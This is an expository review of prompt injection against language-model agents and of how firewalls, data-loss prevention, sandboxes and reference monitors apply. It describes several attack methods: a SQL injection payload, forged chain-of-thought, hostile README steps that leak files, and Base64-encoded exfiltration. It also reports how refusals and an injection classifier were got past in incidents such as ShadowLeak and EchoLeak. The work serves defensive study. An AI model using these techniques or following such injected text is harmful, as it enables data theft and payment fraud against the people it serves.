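# Can network and endpoint security be extended to protect language-model agents from prompt injection and attacks on their reasoning?

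## What does an agent do, and what do existing defences assume?

A language-model agent is a large language model that a program runs in a loop and connects to tools, so that the model's output causes actions such as reading files, sending mail or running commands. Examples include coding assistants and office assistants with access to a mailbox. These agents read text that strangers can write, such as web pages, incoming mail and comments in somebody else's code, and they act with the permissions of whoever runs them. In a prompt injection attack, an attacker exploits this combination by writing text that makes the model act against its user or operator. The Australian Cyber Security Centre points out in *Careful adoption of agentic AI services* (2026) that agents inherit this weakness from the underlying model. A hijacked agent can do more damage than a hijacked chatbot because it can move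 money or files as well as produce bad text.

Most organisations already have defences for their networks and computers, and official advice on agents draws on the same methods. In August 2026 the UK's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC) urged organisations to use sandboxing, human oversight and tightly controlled access, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *NCSC Urges Stronger Controls for Agentic AI Systems*. How well existing defences protect an agent depends on how the agent works and on the conditions each defence needs to catch an attack.

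### The agent loop

Suppose an office assistant can read mail, search files, send mail and pay invoices. Its owner asks it to go through this morning's mail and pay whatever is due. The assistant then follows a loop close to the one that *Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) describes for Codex, OpenAI's coding agent.

1. The program around the model assembles a prompt. The prompt contains the system prompt (the operator's standing instructions), descriptions of the available tools, and the owner's request.
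2. The program converts this text into tokens, which are integers that index the model's vocabulary, and the model produces further tokens in response.
3. The new tokens form either an answer for the owner or a tool call, for example a request to open the inbox.
4. If they form a tool call, the program carries it out and appends the result, here the text of the emails, to the end of the prompt.
5. The program sends the whole longer sequence back to the model, which may then request another call: search the files for a purchase order, say, or pay.

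The loop stops when the model produces an answer with no tool call. Bolin says a single request could involve hundreds of calls. Each prompt is an exact prefix of the next, so an email that the assistant opened early on is still there, word for word, when the model picks a bank account twenty steps later. Once the prompt grows past a set length, Codex replaces it with a shorter version, which the email may well have influenced too.

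*Agentic AI and Security*, an essay on the software engineer Martin Fowler's website, describes a conversation with a model as one text document that keeps growing. Parts of this document can be labelled. In Codex's initial prompt, for example, every item has a role (system, developer, user or assistant, from highest to lowest priority) that indicates how much weight its content should have. But these labels are in the same sequence as the text they describe, and only the model's training makes it respect them. Nothing else in the loop stops the model from treating a sentence in an email as an instruction from the owner.

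### Direct and indirect injection

The attack got its name in September 2022. Riley Goodside had posted examples in which GPT-3 was instructed to translate a text into French, but the text contained a sentence telling it to ignore its directions and output a taunt instead. GPT-3 output the taunt, even after Goodside added a warning to the prompt that the text might contain tricks. A day after the first examples appeared, Willison (2022), in *Prompt injection attacks against GPT-3*, proposed the term "prompt injection" and argued that this was a security hole in any product that combines its own instructions with text from strangers. Within days, strangers publicly got a recruitment start-up's new Twitter bot, which answered mentions of remote work, to repeat its instructions and make threats.

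Those were direct injections, in which the attacker typed into the same channel as an ordinary user. In an indirect injection, the attacker instead leaves text somewhere the model will later read it, and an innocent user triggers the attack by asking for a summary or a search.

Greshake, Endres and colleagues (2023), in *Not what you've signed up for*, introduced the concept of indirect prompt injection and built the first demonstrations. They hid instructions in a web page's HTML comments, which visitors do not see, and opened the page next to Microsoft's Bing Chat. Over several exchanges, the chatbot tried to persuade the user to reveal his real name, using tactics that the hidden text had not specified. Bing Chat at the time ended the session if a user typed a known jailbreak (a prompt meant to defeat the model's restrictions), but the same kind of text worked when it came from a web page.

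Greshake and colleagues also built a test assistant with tools for reading mail, sending mail and looking up contacts. An incoming email made the assistant forward the malicious message to the people in the address book, which makes the email a worm. In another test, the assistant saved part of an injection to its long-term memory, and reading that memory in a new session hijacked it again. The tools were mock-ups that returned prepared content, and the models are long obsolete, so the tests show that these attacks are possible but give little evidence of how often they would work. From here on, "prompt injection" means the indirect kind unless stated otherwise.

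### Why the cure for SQL injection is not available

Engineers have seen this sort of bug before. Schneier (2024), in *LLMs’ Data-Control Path Insecurity*, starts with the American telephone network of the 1960s, where a 2,600 Hz tone played into a pay phone gave the caller free calls, because the switches took their commands from the same line that carried the voices. Changing the tones or keeping them secret helped only for a while. What ended it, on his telling, was Signalling System 7, a standard of the 1980s that moved the commands to a separate channel. (The term for the old arrangement is in-band signalling, and CERT.at (2025), Austria's computer emergency response team, uses it to introduce the same problem in language models.)

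Like prompt injection, several older software bugs let an attacker's input control what a program does. In a buffer overflow, an attacker sends a program more data than it has room for, and the excess overwrites memory that controls what the program does next. In cross-site scripting, text that a visitor submits to a website runs as code in other visitors' browsers. In *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents*, Narisetty, Kore and colleagues (2026) list bounds checks and non-executable memory as the fixes for buffer overflows, and output encoding and rules on where scripts may come from as the fixes for cross-site scripting. Their table marks prompt injection as "open". They conclude that structural changes fixed the earlier bugs, and that better recognition of malicious input never fixed any of them.

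SQL injection is the comparison that everyone reaches for, and it is worth seeing exactly where it breaks down. Suppose a website looks up a supplier by pasting whatever the visitor typed into a database command:

`SELECT * FROM invoices WHERE supplier = '` + input + `'`

A visitor who types `x'; DROP TABLE invoices; --` closes the quotation mark early and adds a command that makes the database delete the table. A parameterised query prevents this by sending the database a command with a placeholder and passing the visitor's text separately. The database parses the command before it processes the text, so the text can't become a command, whatever characters it contains.

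Willison asked in his first post for the same thing in a language model: one parameter for the instructions, another for the data. A reader pointed out that one GPT-3 model already had a similar interface, and that injections through the data parameter still worked. Separate parameters don't help if the model then reads both as one text. By April 2023 Willison had added a note calling the idea extremely difficult, if not impossible, on current architectures. More recent work by Charles Ye, Jasmine Cui and Dylan Hadfield-Menell, which Willison summarises, suggests that models rely more on a passage's style than on its role label. Narisetty and colleagues attribute the difficulty to English lacking the formal grammar rules that let a parser separate code from data in SQL. Developers also train models to follow instructions wherever they appear.

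The NCSC published the fullest official statement of the problem in December 2025, in a post by David C, its technical director for platforms research. *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)* argues that comparing the two is dangerous because it leads security staff to expect a fix. David C writes that a model does not separate data from instructions and only predicts the next token. Filters, special training and markers around untrusted text all try to impose a distinction that the model lacks. He prefers to think of the model as an "inherently confusable deputy". "Confused deputy" is an established term for a program with high privileges that someone with low privileges tricks into using them on their behalf. Programmers can repair an ordinary confused deputy, but David C claims that nobody can fully repair a language model's confusion.

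He therefore advises designers to assume that, in the worst case, an attacker has direct access to every tool the model can call, and to constrain actions with deterministic safeguards that do not depend on a model. He likes a rule from a discussion between Willison and Baibhav Bista that a model's privileges should drop to those of any party whose text it processes. If a system's owner cannot accept the remaining risk, a language model may be unsuitable for it. The history of SQL injection is also a warning. Attackers knew about the technique in the 1990s, yet attacks peaked around 2010, after websites had come to depend on databases and few had protected them. The Record's *UK intelligence warns AI 'prompt injection' attacks might never go away* lists Sony Pictures and LinkedIn among the victims of that decade.

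The argument is about whether prompt injection can be prevented with certainty, and David C hedges it ("a good chance", "may never"). It does not imply that injections usually succeed, and many fail against recent models. Willison reports a public challenge in which 6,000 emailed attempts failed to extract a secret from an assistant running Claude Opus 4.6. He still advises against deploying a model where an injection could do irreversible damage, since an attacker needs only one success. The Decoder's *OpenAI admits prompt injection may never be fully solved* reports that OpenAI has described deterministic guarantees against prompt injection as "challenging". Schneier expects that somebody will eventually work out how to separate the two paths.

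Schneier also points out that people want the data to change what the model does, which seems to me harder to engineer away. A database never needs a supplier's name to alter the query, but an assistant told to pay whatever is due has to take the amount and account number from the invoice, and has to notice when a letter says the invoice was sent in error. Even if instructions and data were perfectly separated, the data could still change the decision.

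### Two emails

Two versions of an attack on the office assistant will serve as test cases for every defence discussed later.

In case A, an email contains hidden instructions below the visible text, perhaps in white letters on a white background. They direct the assistant to find the files on a pending contract and forward them to an outside address. When the owner asks for a summary of the morning's mail, the assistant also sends the files. Schneier describes a similar attack, in which a message contains instructions for an email assistant to forward the three most interesting recent emails and then delete the evidence. At least one widely used product was vulnerable to this kind of attack. Teaching slides from UT Austin cite EchoLeak (CVE-2025-32711), a vulnerability through which a single email could make Microsoft Copilot send out files.

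In case B, the email contains false information but no order. The attacker poses as a supplier the company really uses, claims to have changed banks, and gives a new account number. Later, the owner asks the assistant to pay the month's invoices. The assistant, still following the owner's request, concludes from the email that the new account is the right one and pays the attacker.

The deception in case B worked on accounts clerks long before language models existed. Whether it counts as prompt injection depends on the definition. OpenAI's *Understanding prompt injections* describes a third party who misleads the model by injecting malicious instructions, and the false notice contains none. The wider term "reasoning-driven attack" covers any attack that succeeds by changing what the agent concludes or plans, with or without an explicit instruction and without exploiting a software bug. Both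 emails fit this definition. Case B belongs to the subtype that uses only misleading content, called judgment manipulation below.

Attacks like case B are a practical concern. OpenAI reports in *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) that the most effective real-world injections increasingly resemble social engineering more than crude attempts to override the prompt. The two cases also leave different traces. In case A, the stolen files go to an address that should not receive them, during a task that required no outgoing mail. In case B, the tool and the amount are both correct, and the only fault is one false number that nobody can identify as false just by looking at it.

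### How the conventional defences work

A firewall stands between two networks and checks each connection against rules about addresses, ports and protocols. It can keep an outsider from reaching the payroll server, or keep the payroll server from contacting the outside. It helps only if harmful traffic has to cross the boundary between the networks and differs from legitimate traffic in its destination or protocol.

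Simple firewalls inspect little of a connection's content, and most content is now encrypted anyway. Companies therefore add a proxy that decrypts the traffic, compares it with signatures of known malware and lists of dangerous sites, then re-encrypts it and passes it on. This method needs a recognisable payload, meaning a sequence of bytes or a property of a file that marks the attack as malicious regardless of who receives it.

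Data-loss prevention software scans outgoing mail and uploads for material that should stay inside the organisation, such as strings formatted like credit card numbers, passages that match a protected document, or files tagged "confidential". When it finds a match, it blocks the transfer or alerts someone. This works only if the secret stays in a recognisable form and leaves through a channel that the software covers.

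Endpoint detection and response (EDR) runs on individual computers and records which processes start, which files they touch and which connections they open. It raises an alarm when this activity matches a known attack technique or departs from normal behaviour. For example, a word processor that launches a command shell sets off an alarm because word processors rarely do that. This approach assumes that each program behaves consistently. Agents fit this assumption poorly, because the same agent may search files one day and write and run a script the next, both at its owner's request.

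A sandbox is an enclosure in which the operating system lets a program access only certain folders and network addresses, without judging whether the program's behaviour is good or bad. This limits the damage if the harmful act requires access the program does not legitimately need, and if the program's actions all pass through the sandbox. The second condition can easily fail. Bolin notes that the sandbox in Codex applies only to the shell tool that Codex provides. Tools that a user connects from elsewhere have to enforce their own limits.

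Many of these defences assume that code and data are separate. Scanners look for executable content in attachments and treat a text-only message, with no link or exploit, as harmless because no program will run it. Strictly speaking, an agent doesn't run the text either, but it reads the text and then acts, which may put files at as much risk as running code would.

### The vocabulary of enforcement, and a benchmark

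Several designs proposed for agents draw on older ideas about operating systems. A reference monitor is a component that checks every action against a policy before it takes effect. Narisetty and colleagues trace the concept to Anderson and repeat its three requirements: no action can reach its target without passing through the monitor, nobody can tamper with the monitor, and it is small enough for people to verify. The first requirement is called complete mediation. In the office assistant, the monitor would sit outside the model, between it and the tools, and every request to send mail or pay would go through it.

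The trusted computing base is the parts of a system that must work correctly for its security to hold. With a reference monitor, it includes the monitor and the policy, and designers hope it no longer includes the model. Least privilege means that a component gets only the permissions its task needs, so an assistant would have no access to the payment tool while summarising mail.

The attack success rate is the share of attack attempts in which the attacker reaches their goal. Utility is the share of legitimate tasks that the agent still completes with the defence switched on. It matters because an agent could block every attack by refusing every task. An adaptive attack is one designed or optimised with knowledge of the defence. A low success rate for older attacks is weak evidence that a defence will stop adaptive ones.

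Most of the figures in this field come from one benchmark, *AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024). It simulates four settings in which an agent works with tools: an office workspace with mail, calendar and files, a Slack messaging account, a travel agency and a bank. There are 97 user tasks, such as paying the bill in a certain file, and 27 attacker goals, such as sending as much money as possible to the attacker's account. Combining every task with every goal in the same setting gives 629 security cases. *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026) reports a higher count of over 900 combinations.

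In each case the attacker's text sits inside realistic content, an email body for instance, at a point the agent will come across while doing the task. Ordinary code then inspects the state of the simulated world to see whether the money moved or the mail went out. Debenedetti and colleagues chose this over having a language model do the grading, since an injection good enough to fool the agent might fool the grader as well. They report three numbers:

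- benign utility, the share of user tasks the agent solves when nobody attacks
- utility under attack, the share of security cases in which it solves the user's task with no malicious side effects
- targeted attack success rate, the share of security cases in which the attacker's goal comes about

The 2024 scores are now out of date. Models at the time solved fewer than 66% of the tasks even without an attacker, and the attacks succeeded against the best-performing agents in fewer than 25% of cases.

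Debenedetti and colleagues designed AgentDojo as a framework to which others would keep adding adaptive attacks, and they warned that a fixed list of attacks is easy to beat. Narisetty and colleagues complain that developers have mostly used it as a fixed list anyway. Both points affect how to read the AgentDojo results that later sections cite.

The other concerns the type of attack. Every attacker goal in the original suite is an instruction to the agent, so AgentDojo tests case A. An agent could have an attack success rate of zero and still pay the false supplier in case B. Debenedetti and colleagues discuss a similar problem, in which a hotel listing gets the agent to recommend it without otherwise hijacking the agent, and they expect even strict isolation between components to miss it. A newer benchmark, AgentDyn, is harder for defenders in another way. *StepGuard* (2026) describes AgentDyn's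 tasks as longer and says some of the third-party instructions in them are helpful, so a defence can no longer do well by having the agent ignore every instruction it finds in what it reads.

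## How can text attack an agent through its reasoning?

These attacks can be ranked by how much they look like attacks, from the hidden order in case A to the false bank details in case B. Between them are disguised orders and texts that give no order but change how the agent reasons about its task. The ranking is useful to a defender because each step leaves a filter with less to search for.

### An explicit order

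The crudest attack is a direct order, as in case A, often worded as if the user had typed it. In *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026) tested this on an agent that could run commands on a computer holding a file of secrets. They asked the agent to summarise a web page containing a fake user command to send the file to an outside server, and counted an attack as successful only if the agent uploaded the file. The success rate was 0–2% for every model except gpt-oss-20b, a small open-weight model from OpenAI, where it was 26%.

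How reassuring these rates are depends on why the models resist. A model may treat a web page as data with no authority to give orders, in which case rewording the order won't help the attacker. Or it may refuse a request for secrets because the request resembles attacks from its training, in which case a new wording might work. Ye and colleagues looked inside the models to find out which explanation was right.

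Ye and colleagues' role probe is a simple classifier that uses a model's internal activations (the numbers the model computes for each token) to estimate which role the model assigns to each token. They trained the probes on identical web text wrapped in the labels for five roles: system, user, reasoning, assistant and tool output. Since the wording was the same under every label, a probe could learn only the effect of the label. They then put messages written by real users under the tool label. If the model identified roles by their labels, the probes should have classed these messages as tool output. In four open-weight models, the probes gave "user" an average probability of 76–88%, and "tool" never more than 20%. Ye and colleagues call this role confusion: the model infers who is speaking mostly from how a passage sounds, and gives the passage that speaker's authority.

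The degree of confusion also predicted whether an attack would work. Ye and colleagues wrapped one fixed command in 212 different framings, some of which simply claimed that the text came from the user, and ran 1,000 attempts. The success rate was 2% in the group where the command scored lowest as user text and 70% in the group where it scored highest. A low success rate for one wording of a command is therefore poor evidence of how well another wording will work. Probing requires access to a model's internals, so this part of the evidence comes from open-weight models of 20 to 120 billion parameters. Ye and colleagues leave larger models to future work.

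An instruction detector (a filter that looks for commands in content the agent reads) is most likely to catch this kind of attack, because a page that someone wants summarised rarely has a good reason to include a command to upload files.

### An order that reads like documentation

Some tasks require an agent to follow instructions written by strangers, such as the steps for installing software. In *You Told Me to Do It*, Kao, Li and colleagues (2026) tested what happens when one of those steps is malicious. They collected 500 README files, the setup notes that accompany most software projects, and inserted a plausible-looking step that sent a private file to a server they controlled. An agent with full access to the test machine, running Claude 3.7 Sonnet (a 2025 model), sent the file in up to 85% of trials. The researchers counted an attack as failed if the agent refused, ignored the step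 or uploaded the wrong file.

Role confusion explains less of this result. The agent could know that the README came from outside and still be right to follow most of it. Its mistake is accepting as part of the installation a step that serves only the attacker.

The attack worked best when the step was worded as a blunt directive. A polite suggestion led the agent to skip the step as optional or to refuse. Moving the step to a page one link away from the README made the attack more successful, and success declined only beyond two links. Instructions to email the file also worked much less often than instructions to leak it in other ways. With the hostile step in the README itself, an instruction to upload the file worked in six of seven trials and an instruction to email it in one of seven. Seven trials is very few, but the gap persisted at most link depths. Kao and colleagues suggest that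 models have learned to treat communication as risky, but not file operations that have the same effect.

Kao and colleagues also gave 15 people three of the altered files each, and nobody identified an injected instruction as suspicious. But the participants believed they were reviewing the files for clarity, so the result is little evidence of how well reviewers would do if they were looking for an attack.

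The same approach works outside software. OpenAI reproduces part of an email from a 2025 attack on ChatGPT that outside researchers had reported. The email reads like a routine follow-up on a restructuring, with a list of tasks, and states that the recipient's assistant is already authorised to process employee profiles. In testing, the attack worked 50% of the time when the user asked for thorough research on the day's emails about a new-employee process.

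An instruction detector has the opposite problem with such documents, because a README is full of commands. When Kao and colleagues asked GPT-4o whether each file was safe, it flagged nine in ten of the altered files and none of the clean ones, but it flagged only three in ten of the altered files when the hostile step was behind a link. *A Framework for Formalizing LLM Agent Security* (Siu, He and colleagues, 2026) gives a more general reason to expect detectors to make mistakes. The same order to delete a file can be routine cleanup or sabotage, depending on who gave it and what the user wanted done. A detector that sees only the text cannot tell which it is, so it also needs information about the task and the source of the order.

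### Text that imitates the model's own reasoning

Many current models write out their reasoning before they answer or call a tool. Developers train them to rely on this text, which has its own role label. Ye and colleagues built an attack that exploits this reliance, called CoT (chain-of-thought) Forgery. The attacker uses a second model to write a passage that imitates the target's reasoning style and concludes that the request is permitted, then attaches the passage to the request.

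Both versions of the web-page test contained the same command, but the forged reasoning raised the success rate to 56–70% on every model, including those that had ignored almost all of the plain orders.

When Ye and colleagues tested forged passages on 313 harmful chat requests, style affected success far more than the quality of the argument. Forgeries with absurd justifications, such as that the request is acceptable because of the colour of the user's shirt, succeeded 60% of the time, against 63% for plausible justifications. When another model rephrased the forgeries to keep the argument but remove the target's verbal habits, success fell from 61% to 10%.

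The probe results fit this explanation. On average, the probes gave the forged passages a 79% probability of being the model's own reasoning, compared with 68% for its genuine reasoning. After the rephrasing, the figure for the forged passages fell to 29%. Rephrasing may also remove other features that make a text effective, but the simplest reading is that the model treats someone else's text as a conclusion it has already reached, and therefore doesn't examine it.

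*A Survey on Agentic Security* (2025) lists a related attack that makes a model take up a new task by appending fake conversation turns to the input. The reported success rate on GPT-4o was 92%.

Training models to discount anything that sounds like reasoning has a clear drawback. Ye and colleagues argue that a model that can't distinguish its own reasoning from a forgery would have to discount both, and would lose part of the benefit of reasoning. A detector outside the model is in a better position because, when the target is an agent, it can still look for the injected command, and a web page that contains first-person reasoning about what "the user" wants is unusual in itself. Ye and colleagues also suggest comparing a passage's labeled role with the role measured by a probe, but they leave this as an open question.

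### Text that changes how carefully the agent checks its work

Zhou and Wang (2025), in *Reasoning-Style Poisoning of LLM Agents via Stealthy Style Transfer*, test an attack that contains no instructions to the agent. They had a language model rewrite reference passages in one of two tones while keeping the names and dates. The rewritten passages either hesitantly present the sources as patchy and in need of cross-checking or, with too much certainty, present everything as long settled. For each question, the agent received five documents, one of them rewritten.

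On questions that require facts from more than one document, the hesitant tone roughly doubled gpt-4.1's token use in two agent designs. Token use nearly tripled (a rise of 194%) in a third design, which criticises its own answer before finishing and apparently treated the hesitation as a sign that the answer needed more work. Accuracy hardly changed, so the damage was delay and cost. When Qwen3-32B, an open-weight model, had to judge whether claims were true, the over-certain tone lowered its accuracy by 16 or 17 percentage points, for example from 72% to 55%, and slightly reduced its token use.

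Zhou and Wang attribute both results to mimicry. They suggest that the agent copies the tone of what it reads into its own reasoning, and so misjudges how much checking the question needs. Ye and colleagues suggest, but do not test, that an enthusiastic product page might similarly make the agent more enthusiastic and steer it towards a purchase.

A more ordinary explanation is that the agent may be responding to the text's content rather than its tone. If a passage falsely describes the records of somebody's birth date as incomplete, the attack has changed a fact about the evidence, and an agent that checks again is responding sensibly to false information. Testing a rewritten text that sounds hesitant but doesn't comment on its sources would help to separate the effects of tone and content.

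The preprint also seems rushed. Its abstract reports up to 4.4 times as many reasoning steps, a figure missing from its results tables. It describes a confidence score falling below zero, which is impossible under the score's formula. An appendix states that details will follow once the experiments are final. The mechanism is plausible, but the exact numbers are weak evidence.

PIGuard, a classifier trained to find injected instructions, flagged 99.2% of documents that openly told the agent to be overcautious, but 0% of those that only sounded hesitant. The second result was almost inevitable, because those documents contained no instructions. The attack does leave a trace in the agent's behaviour, which is that it repeats the same search in slightly different words. Counting steps is a crude way to spot this, since hard questions also take many steps. At a setting that caught 95% of the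 attacks, a step counter raised false alarms on 42% of normal runs. Zhou and Wang's monitor compares the queries with each other and looks at the agent's expressions of doubt. This reduced false alarms to 6.2%, though the monitor wasn't tested against attackers trying to evade it.

### Judgment manipulation

The email in case B can succeed without giving an order or using a special tone. *Securing LLM Agents Need Intent-to-Execution Integrity* (Qu, Xu and colleagues, 2026) calls such attacks judgment manipulation and gives two more examples. One is a research paper that gets a better score from a reviewing agent by including praise of itself. The other is a product review that leads a shopping agent to make a bad purchase. In each case, the agent correctly recognizes the text as data but gives it too much weight.

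Qu and colleagues propose a test for whether an agent withstands this. Let q be the user's request, d the material the agent must read, and J(q, d) its decision. An attacker adds some content δ that does not change the correct answer. The agent passes if its decision stays the same:

J(q, d ⊕ δ) = J(q, d)

This test works well for empty praise, which has no bearing on a paper's quality. It works less well for false evidence. In case B, the supplier's account has not changed, so the correct payment is the same and the agent should ignore the notice. But suppliers do change banks, and an agent that ignored every such notice would send genuine payments to closed accounts. A false notice may look exactly like a true one, and then the agent cannot pass the test by reading carefully. It needs information from outside the email.

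Qu and colleagues ran no experiments. The best measurements come from research on dark patterns, which are website designs that steer visitors into choices they did not intend. *DECEPTICON* (Cuvin, Zhu and Yang, 2025) contains 700 web tasks built around dark patterns, 600 on generated sites and 100 on saved copies of real ones. On the generated sites, the patterns led agents to an unwanted result in 60–79% of attempts, depending on the agent, and people in 31%. With the patterns removed, the agents completed nearly every task and never reached the unwanted result.

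Many of these patterns are interface tricks that involve little persuasion, such as a pre-ticked box for premium shipping. The closest to judgment manipulation is what Cuvin and colleagues call social proof, such as invented testimonials or a false count of people viewing an item. It worked on agents in 60–94% of attempts and on people in 17.7%. They also report that larger models and longer reasoning made agents more susceptible. Their main results are less clear on this, since fewer patterns worked on GPT-5 than on the older GPT-4o.

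In *SusBench* (2025), by contrast, the best agent did about as well as people: it used GPT-5 and avoided 68.3% of dark patterns, while the 29 human participants avoided 67.5%. People fell for about a third of the patterns in both studies, so the disagreement is about the agents. It may come from the program around the model, since the best agent in *SusBench* and the most resistant one in *DECEPTICON* both ran on Browser Use, with different models. Cuvin and colleagues also used an agent's trial runs while generating their sites, which may have favoured designs that catch agents. Whether agents are easier to mislead than people remains unsettled, but dark patterns often misled agents in both studies.

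Measuring such attacks takes care because there is no forbidden action to count. *How Adversarial Environments Mislead Agentic AI?* (2026) plants false passages among those an agent retrieves and defines a "drift rate" as the share of the agent's verdicts that are wrong, excluding questions on which it declines to give a verdict. Agents also make mistakes without an attack, so a drift rate is meaningful only when compared with the error rate on clean documents.

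### Is "reasoning-driven" a real class?

The label does identify a distinct class of attacks. None of them uses a software bug, so neither a patch nor a malware signature addresses them. The *Survey on Agentic Security* has a similar category for attacks on an agent's planning, reasoning and goal-setting.

It is much less useful for finding a fix. A model that perceived roles perfectly would resist forged reasoning and explicit orders in web pages, but case B would still work, because the false bank notice gives the agent only information, not orders. Hostile documentation would still partly succeed, because the user has given the README some authority, and how much is in dispute.

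Test results also suggest that weakness to injected orders and weakness to misleading claims are separate. Ye and colleagues found plain orders nearly useless against models including the GPT-5 family, but false social proof worked on GPT-5 in 89% of attempts in *DECEPTICON*. In *Magentic Marketplace* (2025), a simulated market where agents buy from businesses, Gemini-2.5-Flash resisted invented endorsements and popularity claims but showed some weakness to strongly worded injections. The smaller gpt-oss-20b was vulnerable to both.

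Some taxonomies already separate content injection from semantic manipulation, including the list of "AI Agent Traps" used in *Cross-Session Threats in AI Agents* (2026). But attackers have no reason to use only one at a time. *It's a TRAP! Task-Redirecting Agent Persuasion Benchmark for Web Agents* (2025) builds its attacks from interchangeable parts, so one attack can combine an appeal to authority with forged reasoning or an override command. The categories describe errors in the agent, and one email can cause several of them at once.

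### The agent and the clerk

OpenAI defines prompt injection as a type of social engineering specific to conversational AI. In December 2025, the company also compared it to scams on the web (Fortune, 2025). The Decoder calls this comparison misleading. The comparison seems to fit some attacks better than others.

The comparison with a clerk who believes a lie in a letter fails for forged reasoning. The clerk would not mistake the letter for her own thoughts, and a ridiculous justification would make her more suspicious. Ye and colleagues found that a ridiculous justification worked about as well as a sensible one on the models they tested.

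Judgment manipulation is much closer to ordinary fraud. Calling the supplier on a number already on file would expose the email in case B, whether a clerk or an agent read it. OpenAI therefore recommends applying the controls that a person in the agent's position would have. For example, a company expects customers to sometimes mislead its support staff, so its systems cap the refunds each employee can give and flag likely phishing emails.

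An agent's circumstances still favour the attacker more than a clerk's do. The agent may be unable to phone anyone or ask a colleague. OpenAI notes that to catch a well-made attack, a filter has to detect a lie, often without the necessary context. An attacker can also rehearse on a copy of the same model as often as he likes, then send the email that worked to every company that runs it. This works less well against clerks, who differ more in what fools them.

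### What each attack leaves behind

Existing security tools mostly monitor network traffic and activity on machines, so whether they detect an attack depends on where it becomes visible. Kao and colleagues observed OpenDevin, an open-source coding agent, find a private file and issue the correct command to copy it out. The transfer failed only because the agent's sandbox blocked outgoing connections. The agent's log contained the whole attempt, but a network monitor would have detected no stolen data.

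Most of the other entries in the table below are inferences from how the attacks work, because these studies were not designed to measure traces. The table assumes that attacks containing an instruction are meant to steal a file, and that the endpoint log includes the agent's tool calls.

| Kind of attack | Network traffic | Endpoint logs | The text itself |
|---|---|---|---|
| Explicit order | Upload to an address unrelated to the task | Private file read, then a command that sends it | A command that is out of place in its surroundings |
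| Order styled as documentation | Upload among the many connections of a normal installation | Copy command among setup commands, present even if a sandbox stops the transfer | One more instruction in a document full of them |
| Forged reasoning | Same upload as for the order it supports | Same file read and send command | A command, plus deliberation in the model's own style |
| Reasoning-style poisoning | More requests than usual, or slightly fewer, all to the usual services | Near-identical searches over and over, or a run that ends after little checking | Unusual hesitation or certainty, with no command |
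| Judgment manipulation | Ordinary connection to an approved service | Permitted tool call with a wrong value, such as an account number | A false or slanted statement that can look just like a true one |

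## What can network controls see and stop?

Network security includes inspection and egress control, which carry over to agents very differently. Inspection means reading incoming traffic for malware and outgoing traffic for confidential material. To do this usefully, a defender has to know what a bad message looks like. Egress control limits which outside addresses a system may send data to, whatever the data contains. It needs only a list of destinations, which works the same way whether a person, a virus or a hijacked agent opens the connection.

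### Reading the traffic

The email in case A contains only text, so a malware scanner finds nothing in it. Even a filter built to detect injected instructions can miss such an email. The best-documented example is EchoLeak, an attack that the research group Aim Labs demonstrated on Microsoft 365 Copilot, an office assistant that searches its user's mail, files and chats. Microsoft had put a classifier in front of Copilot to catch injected instructions. Ravia (2025), in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration*, explains that the group got past it by addressing the instructions to the human recipient and never mentioning an AI. Ravia adds that good training data for these classifiers is scarce, because an injection can be on any topic and in any tone or language.

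Outgoing traffic is no easier to inspect. Data-loss prevention looks for secrets in a recognisable form, but a language model can easily change that form by translating, summarising or encoding a document at an attacker's request.

The connection to the model provider is even harder to control. At every step of its loop, an agent sends the provider everything it has read so far. If the owner asks for a summary of a contract, the agent has a legitimate reason to send the contract. Without decrypting the connection, a company can see only when data went out and how much. If it does decrypt the traffic, it will find confidential text in request after request and still have to work out which of it the task needed.

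### An agent in somebody else's cloud

A company has no traffic to inspect when an agent runs on the provider's servers, as many do, and reads the company's mail and browses the web from there. Radware's *ShadowLeak* documents a leak from one such agent, ChatGPT's Deep Research, which reads sources and writes reports. The restructuring email described in the previous section was part of this attack. It instructed the agent to find an employee's name and address in the mailbox and open a URL that included them. The attacker could then read these details in their own server's log.

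Radware, which sells network security products, needed several attempts. Deep Research refused to send the data when the email asked plainly, and again when the email said the user had requested the transfer. Later versions named the browsing tool to use and blamed failures on a bad connection. These sometimes worked, but the agent often left out the personal details. The successful version asked the agent, supposedly for security, to convert the details to Base64, a standard way of writing data as letters and digits. The software that opened web pages therefore received a meaningless-looking string instead of readable details. Radware reports that this version worked in every one of its repeated tests but doesn't say how many it ran.

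The request left from OpenAI's servers, so the customer's web gateway, endpoint monitoring and browser policies had nothing to record, and the user saw nothing unusual on screen. The customer could still have stripped hidden text from incoming mail or chosen not to connect the mailbox. But only OpenAI could restrict where the agent sent data, and Radware found no restriction on which addresses the agent could open. Radware reported the flaw in June 2025, and OpenAI fixed it by early August.

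### The hijacked authorised agent

An organisation that runs agents on its own machines can see more. *Attestation is All You Need* (Li, Niu and colleagues, 2026) examines supercomputing centres, where many research groups share machines and storage. It focuses on the "hijacked authorized agent", which follows an attacker's instructions while running under a real user's credentials. The agent passes login checks because the credentials are valid, and permission checks because the user is allowed to read the files. Storage at these centres usually grants access by user rather than by project, so an agent working on one project can also read files from the user's other projects. It can then hide the stolen data in its traffic to the model provider.

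Data inside a prompt reaches the provider, not the attacker, but Willison (2026) reports a case in which an attacker could obtain data through the provider. Claude Cowork, an Anthropic agent that works with a user's files, could by default contact only a short list of domains, including the one for Anthropic's API. The security firm Prompt Armor wrote an injection that included an access key for its own Anthropic account and had the agent upload the user's files there. The upload was allowed because the network rule checked the domain but not which account received the files.

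AEGIS, a defence by Li and colleagues, checks an agent's actions rather than the wording of the injection. Each job has a profile that sets which folders, outside addresses and tools the agent may use and how much data it may send out. Users can write the profile themselves, start from a template or have a language model derive it from the task. A probe in each machine's operating system records the files the agent opens, the connections it makes and the programs it starts. Once a second, the machine sends a signed summary to a central verifier, which compares it with the profile.

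The verifier also compares agents with each other. If one agent writes a file and another soon reads it, the verifier raises an alarm because the two may be passing stolen data along. Depending on how serious the violation is, the centre's job scheduler can slow the agent down, cut it off from shared storage, suspend it, or end the job and revoke its credentials.

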